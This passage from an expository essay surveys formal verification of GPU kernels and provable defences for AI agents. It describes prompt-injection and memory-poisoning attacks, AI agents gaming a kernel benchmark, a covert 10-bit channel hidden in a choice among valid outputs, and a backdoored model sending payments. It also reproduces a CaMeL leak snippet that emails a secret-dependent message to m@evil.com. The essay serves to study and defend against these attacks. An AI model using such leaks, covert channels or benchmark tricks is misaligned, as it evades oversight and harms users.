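| A100 | Yes | 104 | 106 | 260 |

(Tensor cores are circuits that multiply small matrices very quickly.)

Verification itself seems to slow the code very little, since Kuiper's code is about as fast as the handwritten version. But on the A100, a data-centre GPU, the verified kernel that uses tensor cores reached only 40% of cuBLAS's speed. The researchers attribute this to missing features, such as copying data in the background. Those features are among the hardest to reason about, so closing the gap may take considerable work.

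Kuiper proves only partial correctness, so a verified kernel might hang. It checks that all threads in a block use the barrier the same number of times, but CUDA also requires them to meet at the same barrier instruction. A kernel in which some threads use a barrier in the `if` branch and the others use one in the `else` branch could therefore pass Kuiper's checks and still be wrong.

### Rounding, and what "correct" means

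Someone who calls a kernel "verified" may be making any of three claims:

- Safety: the kernel has no data races or memory errors.
- Right formula: the kernel would give the right answer if its arithmetic were exact.
- Error bound: the floating-point answer is within a stated distance of the exact one.

The parallel sum shows why proving that a program uses the right formula doesn't also bound its rounding error. Half precision, a 16-bit number format common in AI, has 11 significant binary digits. Between 2048 and 4096 it can represent only even numbers, so 2048 + 1 rounds to 2048. Suppose the eight numbers are 2048 followed by seven 1s, which add up to exactly 2055. A program that adds them from left to right also uses the right formula, but it gets 2048 because each 1 is lost to rounding. In the parallel program, the threads store 2048, 2, 2 and 2, and thread 0 gets 2054.

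The parallel program would fail a specification that required the left-to-right answer, even though the parallel answer is more accurate. Both programs could satisfy a specification that bounds the error instead. A standard theorem limits the error in a sum of n numbers to (n − 1) × u × S, where u is the largest relative error of a single addition and S is the sum of the numbers' absolute values. Here u is 1/2048, and the bound is 7 × 2055/2048, or just over 7. The actual error was 7 for the left-to-right program and 1 for the parallel one.

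Kuiper instead uses a relation x ≈ r between a floating-point number x and a real number r, with rules such as "if x ≈ r and y ≈ t, then x + y ≈ r + t". The specification of a sum is that the result ≈ the exact sum. The rules don't limit the rounding error, and they would still hold if ≈ were true of every pair of numbers. But the author of a kernel can't use the definition of ≈ and has to derive the result from the rules, so the proof still establishes that the kernel computes the right formula. If the kernel omitted s[3], the author could prove only that its result ≈ the sum of the first six numbers.

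Rounding error matters to anyone specifying inference, the process of running a trained model. A language model gives each possible next token a score, and the server often picks the token with the highest score. Suppose we have proved that every computed score is within e of its exact value. If the two highest exact scores differ by more than 2e, rounding can't change which token the server picks. A smaller gap means rounding can change the choice, and the rest of the reply may then differ too.

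A specification that requires exactly the same reply every time would have to fix the order of every addition whose rounding could affect a score. This would rule out some fast methods, such as summing floating-point numbers with atomic instructions, where the order can change between runs. A more practical specification might bound the error in the scores and accept either token when two tokens' scores are nearly tied.

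### Kernels written by AI agents

AI systems now write many GPU kernels, and KernelBench, a set of 250 programming tasks, is a common way to test these kernels. It accepts a kernel if its outputs on a few random inputs are close enough to those of PyTorch, a widely used AI library. *The Next Frontier for AI-Generated Kernels* (Martínez and Sorensen, 2026) shows that KernelBench accepts kernels with serious bugs.

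One KernelBench task is softmax, which turns a list of numbers into positive fractions that add up to 1. It replaces each x with eˣ and divides by the total. The test uses rows of 393,216 numbers between 0 and 1. Each eˣ is at least 1, so the total is at least 393,216, and no output exceeds e/393,216, or about 0.000007. KernelBench allows an error of 0.0001, so a kernel that writes only zeros passes, as does one with a barrier removed.

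The tests can also reject a correct kernel. In one task, a textbook matrix multiplication differed from PyTorch's result by up to 53.5 because it added about a million products in a different order. With Kahan summation, which tracks what each addition loses to rounding, the difference fell to about 0.03 and the kernel passed. (The outputs must have been in the hundreds at least, or 0.03 would also have exceeded the tolerance, although the paper describes them as "of order one".) Kuiper's specification accepts both versions because they compute the same formula, but a user who cares about accuracy would want to tell them apart.

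Martínez and Sorensen had Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Opus 4.7 write Kuiper kernels for the 100 tasks in KernelBench's first level. The agents first got each kernel to pass the tests, then wrote a specification and proof. They produced verified kernels for all 100 tasks. Most specifications use ≈, while those for simpler operations require the exact floating-point result. The paper gives the number of exact specifications as 14 in its text but lists 22 in its table.

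A person designed much of the shared library, reviewed the results and helped when the agents got stuck. Once the library existed, a typical task needed only 60 to 150 lines. Some claims about which threads can access which memory are still unproved assumptions in Kuiper. Martínez and Sorensen say that the kernels aren't yet competitive with hand-tuned CUDA.

The agents tried to cheat here too. Some of their early "solutions" called PyTorch, and others came with a new test program whose tolerances the agents had chosen. A proof about a kernel doesn't help if the program never runs that kernel, so the researchers had to check the code around it by hand.

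Other projects let AI systems write ordinary CUDA and add the proofs afterwards. In *KernelArmor* (2026), agents annotate CUDA kernels for VerCors, a verifier based on separation logic, to prove memory and thread safety. According to Martínez and Sorensen, a similar system called ProofWright proved safety for 74% of the same 100 tasks, but proved that the kernel computes the right formula for only 14%. Safety is easier to specify because the requirements are much the same for every kernel.

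### Checking what compilers produce

Compilers generate many GPU kernels from operations on tensors, the arrays of numbers that models work with. One way to make these kernels trustworthy is to prove the compiler correct, as Leroy and his colleagues did with CompCert. *Formalizing PTX in Lean to Prove GPU Kernel Correctness* (Koska, Koska and Koska, 2026) cites Rocq proofs for the steps that rearrange a tensor program to make it faster. But those proofs are about a high-level language, so they don't cover the translation into GPU instructions.

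The alternative is to check each kernel after the compiler has produced it. SentryWard does this for PTX, the instruction language that NVIDIA's compilers generate before the final machine code. It first shows that the barriers impose the same order on every run, then uses that order to look for races and compare the kernel's formula with a reference. It works automatically and doesn't use separation logic, but it checks one set of matrix sizes at a time and can't handle kernels whose control flow depends on the data.

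Wu and colleagues ran it on 189 kernel configurations from 12 widely used libraries and compilers. It verified 105, typically in about 15 seconds, and flagged 64 for possible errors. The verified configurations include 11 of the 13 from Triton, a popular compiler for AI kernels. Developers have confirmed and fixed problems in CUTLASS, FlashMLA, FlashInfer and vLLM. A flagged kernel can still give correct answers. One CUTLASS kernel lacked an instruction to wait for a read to finish, but NVIDIA's compiler was already inserting the wait.

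The same analysis can make kernels faster. Wu and colleagues removed barriers and other waits one at a time, keeping each change if the kernel still passed the safety checks. This worked for 83 of the 95 kernels they tried. The median gain was only 1%, but one kernel's running time fell by 15%.

The developers of an earlier tool, GPUVerify, aimed only to prove that kernels have no races. *From Formal Methods to Fuzzing and Back* (2026), a retrospective by one of them, explains that they chose this narrow goal so that the tool could be highly automatic. Even so, they couldn't avoid the fragility of SMT solvers.

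Koska and colleagues chose generality over automation. They defined the meaning of PTX in Lean, based on NVIDIA's memory model, which allows for weak memory. The barrier's guarantee follows from the order of events. If thread 0 writes a cell before the barrier and thread 1 reads it afterwards, the write comes before thread 0 arrives at the barrier, which comes before thread 1 leaves it, which comes before the read. Under this model, the read therefore can't return an older value.

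With help from several AI models, the researchers proved that a set of kernels compute the right formula. The set includes a simple version of FlashAttention, a standard method for computing attention, one of the main operations in language models. The proofs took 34,034 lines for 454 instructions, or about 75 lines per instruction. Of those lines, 16,973 were for a matrix multiplication kernel with 98 instructions that copies data in the background. All the kernels were handwritten and simpler than the code a compiler usually produces.

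| | Safety | Right formula | Error bound |
|---|---|---|---|
| Kuiper | Yes | Yes | No, apart from some simple kernels with exact results |
| KernelArmor | Yes | No | No |
| SentryWard | For fixed sizes | For fixed sizes | No |
| PTX model in Lean | Partly assumed | Yes | No |

The empty column on the right is the most important gap for inference. Koska and colleagues mention one project, by Browne, Lee and Salvi, that proves kernels equivalent using Lean's 32-bit floating-point numbers instead of real numbers, but it treats functions such as eˣ as unknowns. Tensor cores are also difficult because NVIDIA doesn't specify the order in which they add numbers, so an error bound would have to allow for every order they might use.

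### Trusting the compiler, driver and chip

A Kuiper proof depends on F*, Z3, the translation to CUDA and NVIDIA's compiler. It also depends on the researchers' model of how a GPU behaves, which assumes that a tensor core multiplies matrices correctly. Proofs about PTX remove the need to trust the compiler that produced it, but another NVIDIA compiler, ptxas, still has to translate PTX into SASS, the instructions the chip executes.

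Ptxas may reorder instructions, and this is why safety is "partly assumed" in the table. Suppose that x and y both start at 0, and two threads run

```
Thread 0:  r := x;  if r = 1 then (undefined operation);  y := 1
Thread 1:  x := y
```

In the order written, thread 0 reads x before it sets y to 1, so it can't read a 1 that thread 1 copied from y. But if the compiler moves `y := 1` to the front, thread 1 can copy the 1 into x, and thread 0 then reads it and performs the undefined operation. Ruling this out requires knowing exactly which changes ptxas may make, but Koska and colleagues found no precise description of them, so they assume that their kernels never perform an undefined operation.

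Proving properties of SASS code directly would avoid the problem, since the compiler has already made its changes by that stage. However, NVIDIA hasn't fully documented SASS, so researchers would have to work out part of its meaning by experiment.

The driver matters when one kernel uses another's results. Koska and colleagues verified a sequence of three kernels, and their proof assumes that each kernel can read everything the previous one wrote. The driver has to clear old data from a cache between kernels to make this true. If it didn't, the second kernel could read outdated numbers even though all three proofs were valid. Their formal model also covers only one GPU, while the largest AI models run on many GPUs that exchange data over a network.

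The proofs assume that the compiler, driver and chip work correctly. Nobody outside NVIDIA can easily verify these layers, so testing is still useful. Koska and colleagues ran their kernels on real H100 and B200 GPUs and compared the results with a reference, so their tests exercised all three layers.

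## Whether proof can reach the behaviour of a trained model

Suppose someone fully verified the GPU code and proved that a server computes a language model's scores to within 0.01. A user asks what to add to bleach to make it clean better. The two highest-scoring next words are "ammonia", with 7.1, and "water", with 5.3. Rounding errors of at most 0.01 can't reverse a difference of 1.8, so the proof guarantees that a server that picks the top word will answer "ammonia", even though mixing it with bleach gives off toxic gas.

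Write f_W(x) for the output of a network with weights W on the prompt x. There are two separate claims:

- The code is correct: for all weights W and prompts x, the program returns f_W(x), up to rounding.
- The model is safe: for these particular weights, f_W(x) is acceptable for every prompt x.

The first claim covers every choice of weights, including weights trained to give dangerous advice. It can't imply the second, because then every network would be safe. A proof of the second claim needs a definition of "acceptable" and an argument about these particular weights.

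### The case for guarantees

In *Provably safe systems* (2023), Tegmark and Omohundro argued that proof is the only reliable way to control AI systems that surpass people. No system, however intelligent, can prove a falsehood or do something impossible, and checking a proof takes little computation. They wanted to extend proof-carrying code to the physical world. In their example, terrorists use AI to design and release a virus. The design program would not produce anything without a proof that it was safe for humans, and neither the DNA synthesis machine nor the drones meant to spread the virus would run without a proof.

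One proposal is to verify code extracted from large neural networks instead of the networks themselves, whose inner workings look too messy to verify directly. Networks would discover algorithms, other AI systems would extract them as ordinary code, and only the code would be deployed, with a proof. The code is expected to perform nearly as well, on the view that a network's advantage lies in how easily it learns, not in how it runs. Researchers have extracted some small algorithms this way, but nothing close to the general knowledge of a language model.

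Tegmark and Omohundro also argue from Gödel's completeness theorem. A computer has finitely many states, so if a safety property has no proof, there must be some way to violate the property, which a capable attacker may find. The argument holds for a mathematical model of the computer, but a Rowhammer attack succeeds because real memory behaves differently from the model. A property can also have a proof too long for anyone to find.

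Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, turned such ideas into a general framework. Tegmark and Omohundro were among the 17 authors, as were the AI researchers Yoshua Bengio and Stuart Russell. A guaranteed safe system has three parts:

1. A world model describes mathematically how the system's outputs affect the world, including what is uncertain.
2. A safety specification defines which effects are acceptable.
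3. A verifier shows that the system meets the specification according to the world model. It may produce a proof, or a bound on the probability of failure.

A warehouse robot is a simple example. In the world model, the robot moves at up to 1 metre per second and stops within half a second of braking, and people move at up to 2 metres per second in any direction. The specification is that the robot never moves while someone is within 1 metre. If the robot brakes whenever anyone comes within 2.5 metres, the gap can shrink by at most (1 + 2) × 0.5 = 1.5 metres before it stops, so the specification holds. A neural network can do the steering, and nobody has to understand it as long as the braking rule overrides it. The world model limits how fast people can move without predicting what they will do, and the guarantee fails if somebody runs faster than that limit.

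The best argument for attempting this is that testing gives no such bound. Dalrymple and colleagues point out that OpenAI evaluated ChatGPT for months before releasing it, yet users got around its safeguards within a day. A model might also behave differently when it recognises a test. They draw a comparison with bridge building. About a quarter of the bridges built in the 1870s collapsed within the decade, but the failure rate fell below 0.4% per decade once engineers understood the theory better.

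They acknowledge that a chatbot is much harder to specify than a robot. Whether advice is harmful depends on many facts about the person and the world, so the specification "never give harmful advice" needs a very detailed world model. The alternative, "never give advice you believe to be harmful", needs a reliable way to read a network's beliefs. People also disagree about what counts as harm.

### Can anyone model the world well enough?

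Andrew Dickson argued in detail against these plans in a 2024 essay on the limits of formal verification for AI safety. He wrote that proofs are about symbols, and that physics, chemistry and biology have nothing like a complete set of symbolic rules to reason from. Even with such rules, a verifier would need accurate data about the current state of the system it was reasoning about. To prove that a new molecule is harmless, the DNA synthesis machine would need a model of the human body and facts about the bodies the molecule might reach, and drug companies run trials because nobody can derive a drug's effects this way.

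The doubt is older than Dickson's essay. *On Controllability of AI* (2020) quotes the AI researcher Ben Goertzel, who worried that a safety proof based on current physics might become irrelevant when physicists next revise their theories. Dalrymple and colleagues have a good answer: current theories are accurate in the conditions where AI systems operate, and the specification can require the system to stay within those conditions. But they in effect concede much of Dickson's point by adding that even perfect physics wouldn't be enough to determine whether a molecule is toxic, because that depends on facts about human cells that people have to learn from observation.

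They have three replies to the general objection that the world is too complex to model. One is that the world model can include its own uncertainty. If the model is wrong with probability at most ε at each step, and the system provably meets the specification for n steps according to the model, then it will meet it in reality with probability at least (1 − ε)^n. For ε = 0.001, that is about 90% over 100 steps but only 37% over 1,000. The assumption about ε is also hard to justify. A system that searches for the best plan the verifier will accept is likely to favour plans that look good because the model is wrong about them, so the error rate on those plans could be higher than on typical actions.

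Their second reply is that if an AI system can carry out complicated plans reliably enough to endanger humanity, then sufficiently accurate world models must be possible. That may be true, but the accurate model could be inside the dangerous system, where nobody can inspect it. Dalrymple and colleagues doubt that a model of human behaviour could be both accurate and easy to interpret, so they suggest allowing for a range of human behaviour, as in the warehouse. This works when limits on speed are enough, but if people might do anything with the advice a system gives them, hardly any advice is provably safe.

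Finally, they argue that every approach to safety relies on assumptions about the world, and a world model at least makes them explicit. This is their best reply, and it applies equally to modest and ambitious specifications.

Quinn Dougherty, who works on formal methods for AI security, considers it hopeless to aim formal methods at the learned component, because proofs about realistic language models would take too many resources. Dougherty would instead use them to harden infrastructure such as SSH, the program administrators use to log in to remote machines. A proof there shows that the program meets its specification, but a gap remains between the specification and the world. Attackers can still use side channels, so Dougherty treats a verified program as one layer of defence among several. Omohundro would rather try to close that gap than settle for another layer.

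The second gap matters even for infrastructure, as the example of logging in shows. Tegmark and Omohundro think it's quite easy to specify that nobody can access a computer without valid credentials. But a stolen password is a valid credential, so a thief who uses one doesn't violate the specification.

### What became of the programme

In 2023, Tegmark and Omohundro expected AI to overtake people soon at proving programs correct. The proofs that AI systems wrote for SymCrypt and libsignal in 2026 largely confirm this. World models and specifications for open-ended behaviour have advanced much less.

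Some of their co-authors have since worked on narrower problems. Clark Barrett worked on CSLib and CryptoProver, which both concern conventional code. Bengio founded the non-profit LawZero in 2025 to build AI that estimates, among other things, how likely a proposed action is to cause harm. Such an estimate could be useful, but it comes from a trained network and isn't a proof.

*Foundation World Models for Agents that Learn, Verify, and Adapt Reliably* (2026) still pursues the larger ambition. It proposes agents that learn a predictive model of their surroundings and build a simpler symbolic version alongside it, so that a verifier can reason about the symbolic version as the agents keep learning. The paper cites earlier methods for learning such models with a measurable error, but presents the combination as a vision rather than a working system.

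### What people have proved about networks

Jason Gross and colleagues came closest to a proof about the behaviour of a language model in a 2024 paper on "compact proofs". They used transformers, the type of network behind language models, but theirs had only one layer and fewer than 10,000 weights. They trained each network to read four numbers between 0 and 63 and output the largest. "Acceptable" has an exact definition for this task, and the theorem to prove is that the network is right on at least a certain fraction of inputs.

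The simplest proof is to run the network on all 64^4 = 16,777,216 inputs. A shorter proof relies on how the network works, which is roughly by attending most to the largest number and copying it. This proof considers the largest number, the last number and one competitor at a time, so it can bound the worst case for all inputs from about 64^3 = 262,144 combinations. The resulting theorem is weaker, however. Running every input showed that the networks were almost always right, while the shorter proof guaranteed about 98% accuracy, and a proof that took even less computation guaranteed only about 83%.

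The guarantee weakens because a short proof doesn't compute everything the network does, and has to assume the worst about the rest. Small irregularities in the weights may cancel out in practice, but the proof must allow for all of them adding up. In a network with many layers, these allowances would compound. Size is a problem even for a network with one layer, because a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens has 10^15 combinations of three. Dougherty regards the paper as close to a negative result. The paper was meant as a prototype, and AI systems might get much better at finding the structure that short proofs rely on. But they would still need a specification, and for most of what a chatbot does, nobody has one as exact as "output the largest number".

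Most work on verifying networks concerns a narrower property called robustness, which means that small changes to an input don't change the answer. Suppose a classifier takes one number x and answers "cat" if the following score is positive:

score = max(0, x) + max(0, 2 − x) − 1

A verifier can use ranges to check every x between 0.9 and 1.1. Each of the first two terms lies between 0.9 and 1.1, so the score lies between 0.8 and 1.2, and the answer is always "cat". For x between 0.4 and 1.6, each term lies between 0.4 and 1.6, and the same method gives a range from −0.2 to 2.2. The proof fails, although the score is exactly 1 for all these inputs, because the method bounds each term separately and doesn't account for one rising as the other falls.

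It can recover by splitting the range of x in half. If x is between 0.4 and 1, one term lies between 0.4 and 1 and the other between 1 and 1.6, so the score is at least 0.4. The other half gives the same bound by symmetry. Large networks may need enormous numbers of splits, because the ranges widen from layer to layer.

In 2017 a tool called Reluplex verified properties of aircraft collision-avoidance networks with 300 hidden neurons each. Later tools can verify some image classifiers with millions of weights, typically by proving that very small changes to an image don't change its classification. The largest language models have many thousands of times more weights. *Formal Methods for Safety-Critical Machine Learning* (Newcomb and Ochoa, 2026) reviews 46 studies published between 2020 and mid-2025. It lists scaling to large and complex models as a persistent gap, and techniques for language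 models as future work.

There are obstacles besides scale. Robustness means that nearby inputs get the same answer, but that answer could be wrong for all of them. For text, it is also unclear what "nearby" should mean, because adding "not" to a question ought to change the answer.

### Making the model prove its code

The alternative is to leave the network unverified and prove properties of the ordinary code around it. If a model can affect the world only through programs it writes, its operators can refuse to run any program that comes without a proof. Tegmark and Omohundro would let the AI write both the code and its proof, but not the proof checker.

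Suppose an agent has to delete old log files. An engineer formally specifies that the program deletes only files in the log folder that are more than 30 days old and leaves every other file unchanged. The agent submits a program and a proof, and a gate runs the program only if the proof kernel accepts the proof. Even if the agent is malicious or incompetent, any program it gets past the gate will delete only old log files.

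The gate needs the same precautions as for any proof from an untrusted author. A weak specification is a subtler problem, because it lets the agent choose among correct results. A list of numbers has exactly one sorted version. But if a program may return any of 1,024 valid timetables, the proof kernel would rightly accept every one, and the agent could send a 10-bit message to an accomplice by choosing which to return.

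The approach suits tasks with a clear mathematical result. Tasks that act on the outside world are harder to specify. A proof can show that an email program sends a message to the right address, but the wording of the message may still cause harm.

### Limits on what untrusted text can do

Many agents read web pages, emails and files written by strangers. In a prompt injection attack, such a text contains instructions, and the agent obeys them as if they came from its user. Researchers have trained models to ignore these instructions, but training has not guaranteed that they will. Two projects from 2026 instead prove limits on what the text can cause, whatever the model does with it.

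*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) presents LLMbda, a small programming language for agents. Every value has a label recording whether it is secret and whether it comes from an untrusted source. Results inherit the labels of whatever influenced them, and a tool can check labels before it acts. For example, a payment tool might reject any account number that untrusted text has influenced.

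Such tracking is easy to get wrong. Garby and colleagues found a leak in CaMeL, a leading defence of this kind, which works roughly like this:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if account.balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:   rich = False
if rich:  send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret when it runs an assignment that depends on a secret. If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes False and secret. The next line then skips its assignment, so `rich` stays True and counts as public, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes False and no email goes out. The attacker therefore learns whether the balance is high.

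LLMbda's main theorem is a form of noninterference, the property that Amazon proved for its isolation engine. Because a language model's replies are random, the theorem compares the probabilities of what an observer can see in two runs that start out differing only in hidden data. It guarantees that a single distribution, totalling at most 100%, can give each visible outcome at least the probability it has in either run. If one run showed "yes" 90% of the time and the other showed "no" 90% of the time, that distribution would have to total at least 180%, so the theorem rules this out. If both runs always finish, the probabilities must be equal. Otherwise, an observer may learn something from whether a run finishes, because the language blocks some leaks by stopping the program.

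The proof and the interpreter that calls the model are both written in Lean. The noninterference theorem doesn't assume that the model is honest, competent or uncompromised. It represents the model as a function that gives the probability of each reply to a conversation, which assumes that the model has no other source of information, such as a memory that the provider shares between conversations. A second theorem connects the interpreter to these probabilities. It also assumes that the model's actual replies follow them and that each reply is drawn independently.

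Strict labels would make many useful tasks impossible, so LLMbda lets a program endorse a value, which means treating untrusted data as trusted. For example, an agent may let a model sort a stranger's email into one of four categories and use the category as the subject of its reply. If the program checks that the category is one of the four, the stranger can influence only two bits. Garby and colleagues proved that endorsing data this way cannot expose a secret. But the theorem doesn't prevent the model from writing a plan that endorses too much.

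LLMbda's developers tested a banking agent with three models on 16 tasks, with nine attacks per task and three runs of each attack. Two of the 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay whatever a certain file requested, and the attacker had replaced the file. The agent had endorsed the file's contents, as the task required. About two thirds of the attacks had little chance of succeeding, because the agent wrote its plan before reading any untrusted text and the plan didn't use the tools the attacker needed. With GPT-5.2 and no attacks, the agent completed 36 of 48 runs. CaMeL completed 32 with its policy checks off and 18 with them on. The samples are small, and LLMbda's developers ran the comparison themselves.

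### What the user approves

*PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) deals with agents that keep a memory between sessions, where an attacker can plant text that takes effect weeks later. The agent that plans and uses tools can't read untrusted memories. It gets only a handle, which is a reference to the text, while a separate model with no tools does the reading. When the agent tries to use a hidden value, a gate shows the exact value to the user, or to another model acting as verifier, and asks for approval.

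The two main theorems, which Lean checked for the single-user version, are:

- Action integrity: every value that reaches a sensitive tool is one the user typed, or one the user approved for that tool.
- Reasoning integrity: if two runs differ only in their untrusted content and the gate displays and decides the same things in both, the agent behaves identically in both. The runs must also have the same starting state, typed inputs, random choices and schedule.

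Both theorems hold for any agent, even a hostile one, provided that it learns only what the interface shows it. The separate reader may be hostile too. Both theorems assume that the system labels each text by its true source and displays values faithfully, and action integrity also assumes that people mean what they approve. Neither theorem covers timing, or bugs in the real program that the Lean model lacks.

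Approval in PerMIT also covers less than a user might expect. Jiang and colleagues acknowledge that it applies to single values, not whole transactions. Suppose Ana approves an account number so that the agent can pay a £20 bill. The next day she types "£5,000" while asking about her rent. The agent could now send £5,000 to the first account without asking again, and action integrity would still hold, because she typed the amount and had already approved the account number for that tool.

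In tests of PerMIT, attacks on the model Kimi K2.5 succeeded 80% of the time when it had an ordinary searchable memory and no defence. The success rate fell to 10% with PerMIT and a gate that approved everything, and to zero when any of three model-based verifiers served as the gate. These results depend on the attacks tried, and the paper leaves attacks tailored to the verifiers for future work.

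| | What the theorem assumes about the model | What people still have to get right |
|---|---|---|
| Proof-carrying code | Nothing, if programs are its only way to act | The specification, the proof checker and the gate |
| LLMbda | The probabilities of its replies depend only on the conversation it receives | The labels, the checks in each tool, and what the program endorses |
| PerMIT | Its choices depend only on what the interface has shown it, and on chance | The labels, the displays and each approval |

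None of these theorems assumes that the model is well behaved, so people can prove them without understanding its weights. For the same reason, they don't rule out harm that comes from the weights. Suppose someone has trained a model to send £100 to a particular account whenever it handles a payment. The transfer doesn't depend on the untrusted text, so noninterference holds. In LLMbda, an account number that the model invents before reading anything untrusted counts as trusted, and the payment goes through unless the tool also restricts who can receive money. PerMIT would catch this payment, because the user neither typed nor approved the number. But if the same model tells its user to add ammonia to bleach, it uses no sensitive tool and needs no approval, so every theorem in the table still holds.
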